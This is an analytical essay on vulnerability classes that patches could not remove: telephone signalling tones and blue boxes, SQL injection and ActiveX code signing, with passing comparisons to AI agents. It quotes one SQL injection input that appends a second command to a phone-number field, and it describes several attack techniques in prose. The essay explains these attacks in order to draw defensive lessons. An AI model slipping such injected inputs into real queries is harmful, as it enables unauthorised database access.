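# Software features shipped with vulnerability classes that could not be fixed, and what they suggest for AI agents

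## What it means for a vulnerability class to be unfixable

A vulnerability is a weakness in a computer system that an attacker can use to read, change or disable something its owner wants to protect. Most vulnerabilities are mistakes in code, which the maker removes with a patch, a corrected version of the program. Others come from the design of a feature, and no patch removes them for good. Telephone networks, web browsers, Windows and Microsoft Office all shipped features of this kind, and people depended on them for years while attackers exploited them. AI agents, which are language models connected to tools that let them browse, send mail or run code, have the same problem. An agent may carry out instructions that a stranger has hidden in a page it reads.

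In a typical case, a clerk receives an emailed spreadsheet that appears to be a supplier's invoice. She opens it and clicks through whatever warning her version of Excel shows. A macro, which is a small program stored inside the document, then starts, downloads a second program from the internet and installs it. Microsoft built macros so that a spreadsheet could do work for its user, with the user's own access to files and the network. Excel ran this macro as designed, so an engineer would find no error in Excel's code.

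### Definitions, and what they left out

Whether a weakness counts as a vulnerability depends on whose definition applies. Microsoft's *Definition of a Security Vulnerability*, which its security response team used to decide what deserved an update, began with any weakness in a product that could let an attacker compromise the product's integrity, availability or confidentiality. It then excluded weaknesses that exist by design. Under this definition, choosing a weak 40-bit cipher does not create a vulnerability, but a coding error that makes a 256-bit cipher discard half its key does. Microsoft also excluded problems that come from following an imperfect but widely accepted standard, such as a browser transferring files unencrypted over FTP because the FTP specification calls for it. In conference slides, Microsoft (2005) had already listed by-design behaviour among the things that are not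 vulnerabilities.

The exclusion was practical, because the team existed to issue corrections and a design decision has none. But it left the clerk's macro outside the process Microsoft had built to handle security risks.

Definitions have since widened. Microsoft's current *Definition of a Security Vulnerability* adopts the wording of the CVE programme, the international scheme that numbers publicly known vulnerabilities. *Vulnerabilities* (2022), from the US standards agency NIST, uses the same wording, under which the response to a vulnerability can include removing a protocol or function entirely. The CVE Program's *CVE Numbering Authority (CNA) Operational Rules* (2026), in force since 25 August, say that organisations that assign CVE numbers should treat insecure defaults as vulnerabilities. A default is what software does unless a user or administrator changes a setting. The organisations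 may exempt a default that is widely known and consistently well documented, which could cover many notorious features.

A CVE number refers to one flaw in one product. A vulnerability class is a family of flaws with a single underlying cause, and a root fix removes that cause for the whole family. A mitigation makes attacks rarer, harder or less damaging but leaves the cause in place. CERT/CC's *Analysis and Remediation*, guidance from a US centre that coordinates the repair of vulnerabilities, makes the same distinction between eliminating a vulnerability and decreasing its impact, though security writers often use "mitigation" for both. In the clerk's office, a mail filter that catches most malicious spreadsheets and the warning she clicked through are both mitigations.

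That warning is also part of a trust model, the rule by which software decides whether code or content may act. The rule may depend on who signed a program, where a file came from, or what the user clicked. In the clerk's case, it depended on the click. Microsoft's *What IS a security vulnerability, anyway?* reproduces an older definition that counted only flaws users could not guard against "even when using the product properly". A vendor could cite that wording and reply that a careful user would have clicked the other button.

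### Three senses of "unfixable"

People call a vulnerability class unfixable for different reasons. One way to distinguish these reasons is to ask whether the attack would still work if the product had no coding errors.

A complete fix for macros would remove the feature, because the dangerous behaviour is the feature itself. The same is true of ActiveX, Microsoft's system for letting a web page run Windows programs, and of AutoRun, which made Windows start a program when the user inserted a disc or a memory stick. The maker of such a feature can add a warning, narrow the conditions under which it works, turn it off by default or withdraw it. Each option also makes the feature harder to use or unavailable for honest users, so the decision is as much commercial as technical.

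A perfect version of Java or Flash would have avoided most of the vulnerabilities that made them unfixable, but their makers could not find and patch bugs fast enough. Browsers ran both as plugins, separately supplied code for content that the browser could not handle alone. Java confined the programs it ran for web pages to a sandbox, a restricted environment meant to keep them away from the rest of the computer. When an attacker escaped, the cause was usually an ordinary bug, which the maker patched, and then someone found another. *A method to assess 'forgivable' vs 'unforgivable' vulnerabilities*, a paper from the United Kingdom's National Cyber Security Centre, collects figures that help explain why the bugs do not run out. Estimates of the defect rate in software ran from 0.5 per thousand lines of code in 1986 to 1 per thousand in 2019, and one study found that the amount of source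 code in a system doubles about every three and a half years. At one defect per thousand lines, a program of two million lines contains about 2,000 defects, and 4,000 after it has doubled. These are industry averages from separate studies, and only some defects are useful to an attacker. Even so, a maker can keep patching and still fall behind, and a larger budget only slows this.

In the remaining sense, a vulnerability class is unfixable because the medium has no boundary between command and content. Telephone exchanges in the 1950s sent one another orders as audible tones on the same line that carried callers' voices, so a caller who played the right tone could command the network. Engineers call this in-band signalling, in which commands travel through the same channel as content and content can therefore imitate them. Perfect equipment would not have helped, because a caller's tone could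 be identical to an exchange's. Prompts, the text that a language model receives, have the same property. Spreadsheet macros do not, even though they share a file with the data, because Excel can tell a macro from a column of figures and show the figures without running the macro. An exchange could not let the voice through and refuse the tone without moving the orders to another channel.

Several cases fit more than one description. C and C++ are memory-unsafe languages, meaning that they let a program read or write outside the memory set aside for it. Each such error is a separate bug with its own patch, as in Java and Flash, but the languages permit these errors by design. Writing programs in a language that forbids the errors would fix the whole class, but the class is close to unfixable in code that is already in use. NCSC scored eleven ways of preventing common weaknesses by cost, feasibility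 and how well developers know them, on a scale from 3 (easiest) to 9 (hardest). Checking input scored 3, while choosing a different programming language scored 8, the hardest of the eleven. The scores assume that the choice is made at the start of development, and the cost rises sharply for an existing product.

ActiveX fits two senses because it let web pages run programs by design and because those programs had bugs. Email in HTML, the language of web pages, is another mixed case. A mail program that fetches a picture from a remote server while displaying a message is working as intended. If it also puts an attacker's markup and a decrypted private message on the same page without separating them, the missing boundary also contributes to the vulnerability.

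### SQL injection, a class with a root fix

SQL is the language in which programs put questions to databases. SQL injection looked for a time like a problem of the medium, and it turned out to have a root fix. One of the early public accounts came from the pseudonymous hacker rain.forest.puppy (1998), in *NT Web Technology Vulnerabilities*, an article in the hacker magazine *Phrack*. His example was a web page that looks up the owner of a telephone number. The visitor types a number, and the site pastes it into a query:

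`SELECT * FROM phonetable WHERE phone=5551212`

A hostile visitor types a number followed by a command, and the site pastes that in too:

`SELECT * FROM phonetable WHERE phone=5551212 select * from table1`

Microsoft's database of the time, SQL Server 6.5, accepted several commands on one line and ran them all. It received a single string of text, with nothing to mark where the developer's words ended and the visitor's began. According to rain.forest.puppy, a colleague reported this to Microsoft, which replied that it was not a problem.

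The obvious defence is to clean the input. One of Microsoft's own web file formats already tried this by doubling every quotation mark a visitor typed, so that nobody could close a quoted value early and add a command after it. The defence failed on the telephone query because numbers in SQL need no quotation marks, so there was nothing to double. More than 25 years later, *Malicious Cyber Actors Use SQL Injection Vulnerabilities to Compromise Systems* (2024), an alert from the US cybersecurity agency CISA and the FBI, still warned developers that this approach is brittle, hard to enforce at scale and often easy to bypass.

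A parameterised query goes to the cause. The developer writes the command with a gap in it:

`SELECT * FROM phonetable WHERE phone = ?`

The application sends the database a command with a gap in it, and the database works out the command's structure. The application sends the visitor's text separately, as a value for the gap. If the visitor types a number and a command, the database treats all of it as a telephone number and finds no match, or reports an error. However the attacker rewords the text, it never reaches the part of the database that interprets commands, so the defence does not depend on a filter recognising attacks.

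SQL injection could be fixed because the confusion lay in the application. Inside the database engine, running a command and storing a value are different operations, so developers only had to stop combining the two beforehand. ITPro's *FBI and CISA say it's time to delete SQL injection flaws* included a description of SQL as making "no real distinction between the control and data planes", which is fair only for a query written out as one line of text. Language models have no such separation, which is why *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, written by David C for NCSC in December 2025, called the comparison between the two attacks dangerous. The CVE rules make a similar distinction when assigning numbers. If a function can be used securely, each product that uses it insecurely gets its own number, and otherwise a single number covers the function for everyone.

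Parameterised queries took far longer to adopt than to invent. The 1998 article already recommended passing the visitor's input to the database as parameters as the best protection. In February 2000 the same hacker described using much the same method to break into Packet Storm, a website for security specialists, in *How I hacked PacketStorm*. David Litchfield told the Black Hat security conference in 2001 that applications open to injection were "all too common". Litchfield's *Web Application Disassembly with ODBC Error Messages* attributed this to developers who did not understand the problem or had never heard of it. The database MySQL gained prepared statements, its form of the parameterised query, in 2004. David C estimates that the attacks peaked around 2010, and it took a decade of break-ins to produce the better defaults that have made SQL injection rare in websites today.

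A vulnerability class can become rare without disappearing. In 2023 the Cl0p extortion group used SQL injection against a file-transfer product from the company Progress. Security Boulevard's *CISA, FBI Push Software Developers to Eliminate SQL Injection Flaws* (2024) cites the security firm Emsisoft's count of 2,769 organisations and almost 95 million people affected. MITRE's *2025 CWE Top 25 Most Dangerous Software Weaknesses* (2025), a yearly ranking by the non-profit that maintains the standard catalogue of weakness types, puts SQL injection second, up from third the year before.

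That ranking doesn't necessarily contradict David C's "rarely", because the two measure different things. MITRE's ranking is based on 39,080 CVE records, which report flaws in products but don't show how many websites run them. As Steve Christey pointed out in *Unforgivable Vulnerabilities* (2007), such counts also reflect the skill of the researchers who look for flaws and the disclosure habits of vendors. Christey listed 13 kinds of flaw that no competently built product should contain, and NCSC found that most of them still exist in some form.

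SQL injection persists because a fix for its root cause protects only the code that uses it. Microsoft could change how Windows handled memory sticks by sending out an update, whereas nobody could rewrite the queries in everyone else's programs.

### Five questions for each case

One can put the same questions to every case from telephone tones to memory-unsafe languages.

1. What made the flaw permanent? The answer limits the remedies. A feature that is itself the danger leaves its maker choosing among restrictions, while a missing boundary calls for a new channel or a new medium.
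2. Which trust model did the maker rely on? A signature, a place of origin and a click each hand the decision to somebody, and often to the person least able to make it.
3. How many years passed between the first public demonstration and a changed default? Insiders may have known earlier, but a public demonstration has a date. The changed default is the better end point because an optional safe setting protects only those who go and find it. For SQL injection the interval has no clear end, since every developer set the default anew.
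4. What forced the change? Candidates include a wave of infections, pressure from customers, a rival technology and the decision of some other company that controlled the platform.
5. Where did attackers go next? Closing one route may bring displacement, a move to another. This is the hardest of the five to answer, because attackers also change their methods for reasons of their own, and a fall in one technique beside a rise in another does not prove that the first caused the second.

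The choice of cases is biased, because all of them are famous for having gone badly. A feature with an equally weak design leaves little trace if its maker quietly restricted it before attackers took an interest, or if attackers never did. Unencrypted protocols come close to being an example. Microsoft once used plain-text FTP to illustrate what was not a vulnerability, and the CVE Program now cites changed attitudes to plain-text protocols as grounds for recording new vulnerabilities, but the shift produced no episode as famous as the macro viruses. A list of famous failures therefore probably overstates how often a flawed design ends in mass attacks and a forced retirement, and it can't be used to estimate the odds for any new feature. Estimating those odds would require starting from every product that shipped with a known design weakness, including the many that nobody has had reason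 to write about.

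## Telephone signalling tones and blue boxes, 1950s to 1980s

For most of the twentieth century the American Telephone and Telegraph Company (AT&T) provided most telephone service in the United States, through a group of companies known as the Bell System. Operators at switchboards connected long-distance calls by hand. According to *Phreaking Politics in Modern America* (Bruggeman, 2026), AT&T's managers and engineers concluded after the Second World War that operators could never keep up with demand and that machines would have to make the connections. An exchange in New York then needed a way to signal to one in Miami that a call was coming, which number the caller wanted and when the call had ended.

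### How the tones worked

Exchanges already signalled to their neighbours by switching a direct current on and off, but this worked only over fairly short distances, and many long-distance lines could not carry direct current at all. *In-Band Single-Frequency Signaling* (Weaver and Newell, 1954) described the Bell System's replacement, which used sound. While a trunk (a line between two exchanges) was idle, equipment at each end sent a steady tone along it. To start a call, the exchange stopped its tone, and the equipment at the far end prepared to receive a number. When the caller hung up, the tone came back and the far exchange released the line. The newer version used a tone of 2,600 hertz, a high whistle well within the range that a telephone line carries. A separate set of tones, each made of two frequencies sounded together, could carry the digits of the number.

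These signals travelled on the same circuit as the conversation, so a caller could send them too. A caller would dial a toll-free number in another city, and the local exchange would connect the call to a trunk. The caller then played 2,600 hertz into the mouthpiece, and the far exchange dropped the call, because that tone meant the trunk was idle. When the tone stopped, the far exchange prepared for a new call and accepted whatever digits the caller sent in the network's own tones. The local exchange, which handled the billing, had recorded only one call to a free number. In 1974 a federal judge, Snyder, summarised a case of this kind in *Opinion and Order*. Prosecutors had charged a man on eleven counts with calling toll-free numbers from a Pittsburgh telephone and using the 2,600-hertz tone to get past the billing system.

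Weaver and Newell knew that other sounds could imitate the signal, but they treated this as a problem of accidents. In one series of observations on lines from New York, they counted 69 false signals, of which speech caused 48, circuit faults 10 and adults whistling 2. At 2,600 hertz, over 90 per cent of the imitations by speech came from the long "e" in words such as "feet". They chose a high frequency because false signals became rarer as the pitch rose. They also gave the receiver what they called guard action, in which sound at other frequencies produced a voltage that opposed the one from the signal tone. Since speech spreads its energy over many frequencies, a customer's talking usually did not trigger the receiver. A pure 2,600-hertz tone produced no opposing voltage, whether it came from an exchange or a customer.

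Weaver and Newell mention two other Bell System signalling methods, one that used a separate channel and another that used a tone of 3,700 cycles, just above the voice band. They called these systems out-of-band because the commands travelled outside the space available to the caller. The in-band system worked on any line good enough for conversation, whatever its length, and needed no extra bandwidth or new equipment along the route. The 2,600-hertz unit was also half the size of the older 1,600-hertz one and cost less than half as much. Leaving out a boundary between command and content therefore saved money across a continental network. Critics now say that language models lack this boundary too.

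### How the design became public

AT&T itself published the design. The historian Phil Lapsley, in *Some Historical Documents* on his Exploding the Phone website, lists a 1949 engineering paper as the earliest public description he knows of the tones that carried the digits. Weaver and Newell's article on the idle tone followed in the *Bell System Technical Journal* in 1954, and in November 1960 the same journal printed *Signaling Systems for Control of Telephone Switching*, a survey of the whole subject. The Computer History Museum's catalogue entry *Telephone "Blue Box"* says that the 1954 and 1960 articles together revealed the weakness. According to Bruggeman, Bell also reached a wider public through an advertisement in *Popular Mechanics* that likened automatic dialling to playing a tune on a keyboard, and a film, *Speeding Speech*, that included the tones themselves.

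Bell had reasons to publish its signalling methods. The network belonged partly to independent telephone companies, whose engineers had to build equipment that worked with Bell's. AT&T's *Notes on the Network* (1980) still set out technical requirements for what it called the Bell and Independent Network. A signalling method that thousands of engineers must know is hard to keep secret anyway. Bruggeman adds that a monopoly had no competitors to hide its methods from.

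Ralph Barclay, an 18-year-old engineering student, came across the November 1960 issue in his college library. Washington State Magazine, drawing on Lapsley's research, reports that within weeks he had used a battery, a rotary dial and a single transistor to build a device that made the 2,600-hertz tone. He then built a better version with a keypad from an adding machine. Its metal case was blue, and people came to call all such devices blue boxes, whatever their colour. The following summer the police arrested Barclay. A court gave him a suspended sentence for making a call without paying, and he gave up the hobby. AT&T later concluded that his was the first blue box, though Lapsley dates the first known break-in by this method to the mid-1950s. A ten-minute call from Miami to Denver then cost $5.90, which Lapsley put at about $48 in early-2010s money.

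Joe Engressia, a blind student with perfect pitch, could whistle the tone, and a toy whistle from a box of Cap'n Crunch cereal also produced it. By the late 1960s enthusiasts had found one another, and they came to call themselves phone phreaks. *Secrets of the Little Blue Box* (Rosenbaum, 1971) brought them to a national audience when *Esquire* published it in October 1971. The article profiled a maker of the devices, under the false name Al Gilbertson, who said he had built his first working box within about twelve hours of finding the tones in a Bell journal.

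By then, Gilbertson claimed, Bell had withdrawn that issue from engineering libraries. If so, the withdrawal had little effect. In Nieman Storyboard's *Annotation Tuesday! Ron Rosenbaum and "The Secrets of the Little Blue Box"*, an interview published with the article's text, Rosenbaum recalls that he deliberately left out some of the codes, and that Steve Wozniak and Steve Jobs, who later founded Apple, found the rest in an engineering journal. They built boxes and sold them for about $6,000 in all, according to the *New York Times* obituary of Jobs that *Slate* cites in its reprint.

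Blue boxes soon attracted people with political or practical motives. The political activist Abbie Hoffman co-founded a newsletter in 1971 that printed instructions for blue boxes as a form of protest against AT&T. Bookmakers and some businessmen and actors valued the free long-distance calls. Gilbertson boasted that a Las Vegas syndicate had ordered a thousand boxes from him. His word is the only evidence for that order, but in 1973 the FBI arrested a gambler in a Las Vegas telephone booth with two boxes and more than $18,000 in cash. By the mid-1970s, Bruggeman writes, front-page reports in the *Wall Street Journal* suggested that tens of thousands of Americans had dabbled in phreaking.

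### What the fraud cost

| Estimate | What it covers | Where it comes from |
|---|---|---|
| About $1 million a year | Losses that AT&T could prove from electronic devices | AT&T's own magazine, 1978 |
| About $27 million in 1977 | All known long-distance fraud, including false credit card numbers | AT&T's own magazine, 1978 |
| $50 million a year | Phreaking | An internal memo, as Rosenbaum later heard of it |

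The lower two figures appear in AT&T's magazine, where Gum and Oxford, in *Fun with Dick and Jane*, warned that the real total for electronic devices might be many times the $1 million that could be proved. Gum was a public relations supervisor at AT&T, which was then supporting a federal ban on the devices, so both had reason to stress the scale of the problem. A newspaper article of April 1978, *Captain Crunch’s secrets, or beating the phone system*, adds that the $27 million was only what AT&T knew about. The $50 million figure is the weakest of the three because Rosenbaum mentions it at second hand, without a date, and it is nearly twice what AT&T reported for every kind of toll fraud in 1977.

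None of these figures measures what the calls cost AT&T to carry. An enthusiast who called a recorded weather forecast in Tokyo would seldom have paid to make the call, and one phreak told the company's magazine that he worked late at night to avoid tying up lines. A bookmaker who made hours of calls every day was more likely to have cost AT&T revenue. In either case the sums were small compared with AT&T's income. Bruggeman estimates that income at $16 million a day around 1960, so even the full $27 million for 1977 was less than two days' income at the 1960 rate.

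### Detection, monitoring and prosecution

AT&T first responded by looking for the people using the tones. Gum and Oxford report that Bell Laboratories developed automatic units in the early 1960s to scan trunks for signs of electronic fraud, and they stress that the scanning was mechanical and that the company put privacy first. In an interview with Lapsley, *What todays hackers owe phone phreaks*, the interviewer describes a secret AT&T project called Greenstar, begun in 1962, as wiretapping "literally millions" of customers. The dates suggest that both accounts concern the same programme, although Gum and Oxford never use the name. Whether or not this counted as wiretapping, AT&T had to monitor the voice channel to find false commands, because the network carried its commands there.

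Testimony to the National Wiretap Commission in the 1970s, reprinted in Full Disclosure's *Death of the Blue Box* (1991), describes how a Las Vegas telephone company investigated blue box use. The company searched its computer records for implausible calls, such as a half-hour call to an airline's enquiry line, then recorded the suspect's line to confirm that someone was using a blue box. The FBI obtained a search warrant, waited for the company to report that the box was in use, and sent agents in. Between April and October 1973 the company gave the FBI about 32 telephone numbers. Five cases led to indictments, and federal prosecutors declined seven others, including that of a man who had built a box so that his wife could call her mother in Miami once a week.

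The witnesses doubted that the method would work elsewhere. Las Vegas had low buildings and wide streets. An FBI agent with ten years' experience in Chicago thought it almost impossible to reach an apartment in a large city before a call ended. Investigators also had to show who had used the blue box, because federal law did not prohibit owning one. William Caming, a lawyer for AT&T, estimated that the company had about a thousand cases in a decade. One case, against a ring of manufacturers, distributors and users, required the cooperation of 16 telephone companies and led to 20 arrests.

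Prosecution did become more efficient. Gum and Oxford count 160 arrests and 144 convictions in 1976, a conviction rate of 90 per cent. But after each conviction the tone still worked for everyone else, and some convicted users offended again. John Draper, nicknamed Captain Crunch after the cereal whistle, received five years' probation after his arrest in 1972. He went back to jail for toll fraud in 1977, according to TechRadar, and Gum and Oxford report another sentence in 1978. The risk of arrest probably kept most customers from trying, which may be why the provable losses stayed small.

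### A separate channel

Moving the commands off the voice circuit fixed the root problem. In common-channel signalling, two exchanges send each other instructions over a separate data link, which serves many conversations and has no connection to callers' lines. If someone whistles 2,600 hertz into a call set up this way, the person at the other end hears it, but the exchange does not respond.

AT&T began to install its version, common channel interoffice signalling, in 1976, about fifteen years after Barclay's arrest. Its engineers presented the change mainly as an improvement in performance. *Common Channel Interoffice Signaling* (1978), an article from Bell Laboratories, cites the limitations of the older systems and the need for faster signalling and much greater capacity. According to the article, the idea was not new, but only recent technology had made it practical on a large scale.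 The limitations may have included fraud, but provable losses of a million dollars a year probably would not have justified the expense of rebuilding a national network without the gain in speed.

AT&T controlled most of the equipment that had to change, an advantage that database makers lacked with SQL injection. Customers could keep their telephones and dial as before. But the work took decades, because both ends of a trunk had to support the new method and an exchange still needed the old tones to reach places that had not converted. Single-frequency signalling had largely disappeared by the end of the century, though isolated rural routes kept it into the 2000s. Callers in Europe were still blue-boxing in the early 1990s, through toll-free numbers that led to countries whose international lines used in-band tones.

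Phreaking in the United States had declined by then, only partly because of the separate channel. Bruggeman also points to prosecutions, the break-up of the Bell System in 1984 and home computers, which drew many phreaks away. Closing the voice channel to commands did not stop kinds of telephone fraud that never depended on the tones, such as using stolen credit card numbers and lying to operators. Those two methods had accounted for most of AT&T's known losses even while blue boxes worked.

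### SS7 and the missing check on identity

In 1980 the international standards body for telephony adopted Signalling System No. 7 (SS7), which became the common protocol for separate signalling networks around the world. SS7 prevented callers from sending commands to the network, but it had no way to verify that the operator sending a command had the right to give it. When the network connected a small number of large, mostly national telephone companies, access to it was a reasonable substitute for proof of identity. Access became a weaker substitute as governments opened their markets and many more companies, some of them resellers, gained connections.

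Mobile telephones made the gap more useful to attackers. When a customer travels abroad, the foreign operator sends the home operator a message that the phone is now on its network, and the home operator redirects calls and texts there. Someone with access to SS7 can send the same message about a phone that has never left home. In 2014 the German researchers Tobias Engel and Karsten Nohl separately demonstrated that outsiders could use SS7 to track phones and intercept calls. In 2017 the German operator O2-Telefónica confirmed that thieves had used it to redirect text messages containing bank security codes. The thieves already had the victims' passwords, and the codes let them approve transfers out of the accounts.

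Separating signalling from speech controls which channel can carry a command, but establishing who sent the command requires authentication. The 1954 system had neither, and common-channel signalling supplied only separation. That defeated the blue box, which worked only from a caller's line, but gave no protection against an attacker who obtained an operator's connection. Mobile operators have since added filters that reject implausible messages, such as a report that a phone has appeared abroad minutes after making a call at home. These filters are only mitigations, because a forged message about a customer who really is travelling may pass as plausible.

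## ActiveX and the limits of code signing, from 1996

The telephone network could not verify that a command came from someone with the right to send it. Microsoft did include a check on identity in 1996, when its Internet Explorer browser began letting web pages install programs, called ActiveX controls, on visitors' computers. Each control could carry a digital signature that showed visitors who had published it. Attackers found ways to use ActiveX even though the signatures mostly worked as Microsoft intended.

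### Native code on a web page

A control let a web page do things that ordinary pages of the time could not, such as play a video or run a small spreadsheet. The page named the control by its class identifier, a long number, and could give an address to download it from. Internet Explorer looked the number up in the registry, where Windows keeps its settings. If the number was there, the browser ran the control. Otherwise it downloaded the control, asked the user's permission and installed it. The control then stayed on the computer, where any other web page could try to use it.

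ActiveX controls were native code, which the processor runs directly. In August 2000 CERT/CC invited twenty experts to Pittsburgh to discuss the risks. CERT Coordination Center's *Results of the Security in ActiveX Workshop* (2000) describes a control as code that runs without a sandbox and can take any action the user can take. Microsoft gave controls this freedom on purpose. Its *Frequently Asked Questions About Authenticode* (1996) says that a sandbox like the one that confined Java applets was unlikely ever to allow enough for many applications.

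### What Authenticode checked

Authenticode was Microsoft's system of code signing, in which a digital signature shows who published a program and that nobody has altered it since it was signed. It worked in five steps.

1. The publisher created a pair of matching keys, one private and one public, and applied to a certificate authority such as VeriSign. The authority checked the applicant's identity and issued a certificate that tied the publisher's name to the public key. VeriSign charged companies $400 a year and individuals $20, and applicants pledged not to sign malicious code.
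2. The publisher ran the finished program through a hash function, which reduces a file of any size to a short digest. It encrypted the digest with the private key and attached the result to the program, along with the certificate.
3. When a user downloaded the program, Windows decrypted the digest with the public key and computed a fresh digest from the file. If the two matched, nobody had changed the file since the publisher signed it.
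4. Internet Explorer displayed the publisher's name and asked whether to go ahead. The user could also choose to accept everything from that publisher in future without being asked.
5. If the user agreed, the control installed itself and ran with all of the user's rights.

A valid signature proves that someone with the certificate's private key signed this exact file. It does not show that the publisher is honest or competent, which Microsoft acknowledged from the start. It also does not show what the program can do, whether a newer version has replaced it, or whether the website offering it is connected to the publisher.

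Even the publisher's name in a signature is only as reliable as the certificate authority. According to ITPro Today's *Erroneous VeriSign-Issued Digital Certificates* (2001), VeriSign issued two certificates on 30 and 31 January 2001 to someone who falsely claimed to work for Microsoft. VeriSign revoked them, but they lacked the address where a browser would look for the list of revoked certificates. Microsoft pointed out that Windows would still show a warning before running anything signed with them, but conceded that even a security-conscious user might click yes.

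### Internet Exploder

On 17 June 1996 the programmer Fred McLain posted Internet Exploder, an ActiveX control that shut down Windows 95 and switched off the computer. He signed it on 23 August with an individual VeriSign certificate, according to Microsoft's *What Is the Exploder Control and How Does It Relate to Authenticode?* (1996). By default, Internet Explorer refused unsigned controls but offered signed ones, so the signature made the control available to ordinary visitors. McLain's point was that it could as easily have erased their disks.

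Microsoft replied that Authenticode proved who had published the control, so victims could hold McLain accountable. After several weeks of argument, VeriSign revoked his certificate, the first time it had done so without the holder's consent. According to *ActiveX and Authenticode*, from O'Reilly's guide to web security, the revocation had little effect at first because Internet Explorer could not check whether a certificate was still valid until version 3.0.1.

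Supporters of ActiveX said that the system had identified a hostile publisher and contained the damage. But McLain was easy to catch because he had signed under his own name and wanted people to notice. A quieter control could have copied files for months and then deleted itself, and Internet Explorer kept no detailed log of the controls it had run. In January 1997 the Chaos Computer Club, a German hackers' association, showed on television what such a control might do. *Electronic Funds Transfer without stealing PIN/TAN* (Weber-Wulff, 1997), citing a Berlin newspaper, reports that visiting a web page was enough to start a control that looked for the finance program Quicken and gave it a transfer order. Microsoft responded in part by warning users to be careful about what they downloaded, according to American Banker's *Internet Banking Hits Another Security Snag*.

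That same month a programmer wrote that ActiveX had no real security architecture and at best a "blame-assignment architecture", a judgement repeated years later in the weblog post *Microsoft says: Don't trust Microsoft*. The phrase describes Microsoft's argument fairly well. Blame may deter a company with a reputation to lose, but it does little to deter a stranger with a $20 certificate. Victims would have to trace the damage to a particular control, identify its publisher, find a court with jurisdiction and pay for a lawsuit. O'Reilly doubted that many would manage it.

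### One decision for everything

The user made one choice, which covered everything the control might do. Internet Explorer could not let a control play video while keeping it away from the user's documents, because Windows had no way to restrict one control from outside. The experts in Pittsburgh thought the decision to install software should ideally depend on what it could do, but users had only the name of its presumed source. A user who needed one control that its author had not marked as safe for web pages had to set Internet Explorer to permit all such controls.

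The prompts also wore people down. In *Re: Active X exploit*, a reply on the Bugtraq security mailing list, Donnerhacke (1997) complained that the browser did not remember a refusal. Anyone who declined Microsoft's controls while using its website was asked again every couple of seconds, and he concluded that people lowered their security settings or accepted something by accident.

The journalist Larry Seltzer thought critics exaggerated the dangers of ActiveX. In *The Lame Blame of ActiveX* (2005), he recalled a demonstration of Internet Exploder at a conference for Java developers, where the presenter hit Enter so fast that the audience hardly saw the warnings. Seltzer called this dishonest, with some justice, but an impatient user who wants to see a page does much the same thing. He also acknowledged that users needed an easier way to understand what a signature proved, and that some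 makers of adware, software that shows unwanted advertising, had put misleading company names in their signatures. Since a control without a valid signature never reached the prompt, *How VeriSign Could Stop Drive-By Downloads* (2005) argued that VeriSign had the power to block such software.

### Safer than the shop?

Defenders of ActiveX compared it with ordinary software. Paul Leach, whose message prompted Donnerhacke's reply, wrote that users ran a control only if they trusted the signer, and that they knew nobody had tampered with it: "That's more secure than what I buy at the store." He was right about tampering, because a criminal can counterfeit a box more easily than a signature. The Pittsburgh experts also compared a signature to shrink-wrap, but their point was that neither shows the buyer whether the program inside is any good.

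The comparison fails after installation, because any website could start an installed control and supply its instructions, whereas a program from a shop normally runs when its owner starts it. O'Reilly gives the example of a control that a reputable company writes to delete temporary files. If the web page tells the control which file to delete, a hostile page can name an important one. Security engineers call such a program a confused deputy, because someone who lacks its privileges tricks it into using them. The signature is genuine, and any investigation leads to the company that wrote the control rather than to the attacker.

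Microsoft's protection against the misuse of legitimate controls was two labels, "safe for scripting" and "safe for initialization", which each control's developer applied. Developers, including Microsoft's, mislabelled controls. CERT Coordination Center's *Office 2000 UA Control incorrectly marked safe for scripting* (2000) warned that a web page or an email could use one mislabelled control to switch off the macro warnings in Office. The Pittsburgh experts considered such misuse a much greater concern than hostile controls, of which they knew very few.

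Seltzer believed he could count on two hands the Internet Explorer vulnerabilities involving ActiveX. Three years later, a test by two CERT/CC researchers suggested that there were many more. Dormann and Plakosh, in *Vulnerability Detection in ActiveX Controls through Automated Fuzz Testing*, collected 5,956 controls that web users had downloaded, and found that 3,097 carried at least one of the two labels developers used to mark a control as safe. They fed these controls malformed input, such as a string of ten thousand letters. The tests looked only for the simplest errors, but they crashed 705 of the controls, and 284, about one in eleven of those tested, crashed in a way that an attacker could probably exploit.

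### Signatures that outlived the fix

When a publisher fixed a faulty control, the old version kept its signature. The researcher Juan Carlos García Cuartango pointed this out in 1999 about a control that Microsoft had signed, and said the hole might exist forever even if Microsoft fixed it. Georgi Guninski tested the idea in *Digitally signing buggy ActiveX components* (2002). He put an old, faulty Office control on a web server and had a page offer it to a computer that already had the corrected one. Internet Explorer correctly reported that Microsoft had signed it, and once the user agreed, the old attack worked again. A user who had chosen to trust everything from Microsoft would not have been asked.

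In November 2002, Microsoft rated as critical a flaw in its Data Access Components, very widely shipped software that programs use to reach databases, and issued a corrected control (Microsoft, 2002). Websites could still request the vulnerable version, however, and Internet Explorer would reinstall it. In *Don't Trust Me*, the blogger marco quoted the bulletin's advice to "make sure you have no trusted publishers, including Microsoft". Microsoft could have blocked the control outright, but according to marco it hesitated because so many websites referred to it.

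### The kill bit

Microsoft blocked a control by setting its kill bit, a registry entry that tells Internet Explorer never to load the control with that class identifier. No other browser setting overrides it. Because the block applies to the identifier, it also stops old signed copies from running, which releasing a corrected version alone could not do. But each kill bit covers only one control, and Microsoft could set it only after someone had found the flaw.

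Setting a kill bit to block a control also took less work than repairing it. Microsoft's *Internet Explorer's ActiveX Security Mitigations in Use* explains that when a malicious page could exploit the company's own video control, which should never have been available to web pages, Microsoft set the control's kill bit and left its code alone. But blocking a control could break other features. Microsoft (2008) described a control that could leak email addresses, for which a kill bit seemed the right answer until testing showed that it partly broke Remote Assistance, the Windows feature for helping someone at a distance. Browsers could also fail to enforce the block. CERT Coordination Center's *Microsoft Internet Explorer does not honor ActiveX kill bit* (2006) warned that a specially written page could make the browser skip the kill bit check.

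A larger weakness was that the faulty controls stayed on the computer. Microsoft's *The Kill-Bit FAQ* (2008) confirmed that other programs could still load a blocked control unless they too checked the list of blocked controls. *No Loitering*, a study by Dewey and Traynor from IBM and the Georgia Institute of Technology, published at the security conference NDSS, found about 600 entries on the list and concluded that Microsoft had left most of those controls unrepaired. Microsoft Word checked the list before loading a control, but it did not check what that control then loaded. The researchers built a Word document in which a harmless control for choosing dates loaded a blocked one. Word showed no warning, and they could run commands on the computer. They compromised fully patched versions of Windows XP, Vista and 7 through blocked controls, and the method also worked in Excel, PowerPoint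 and Adobe Reader.

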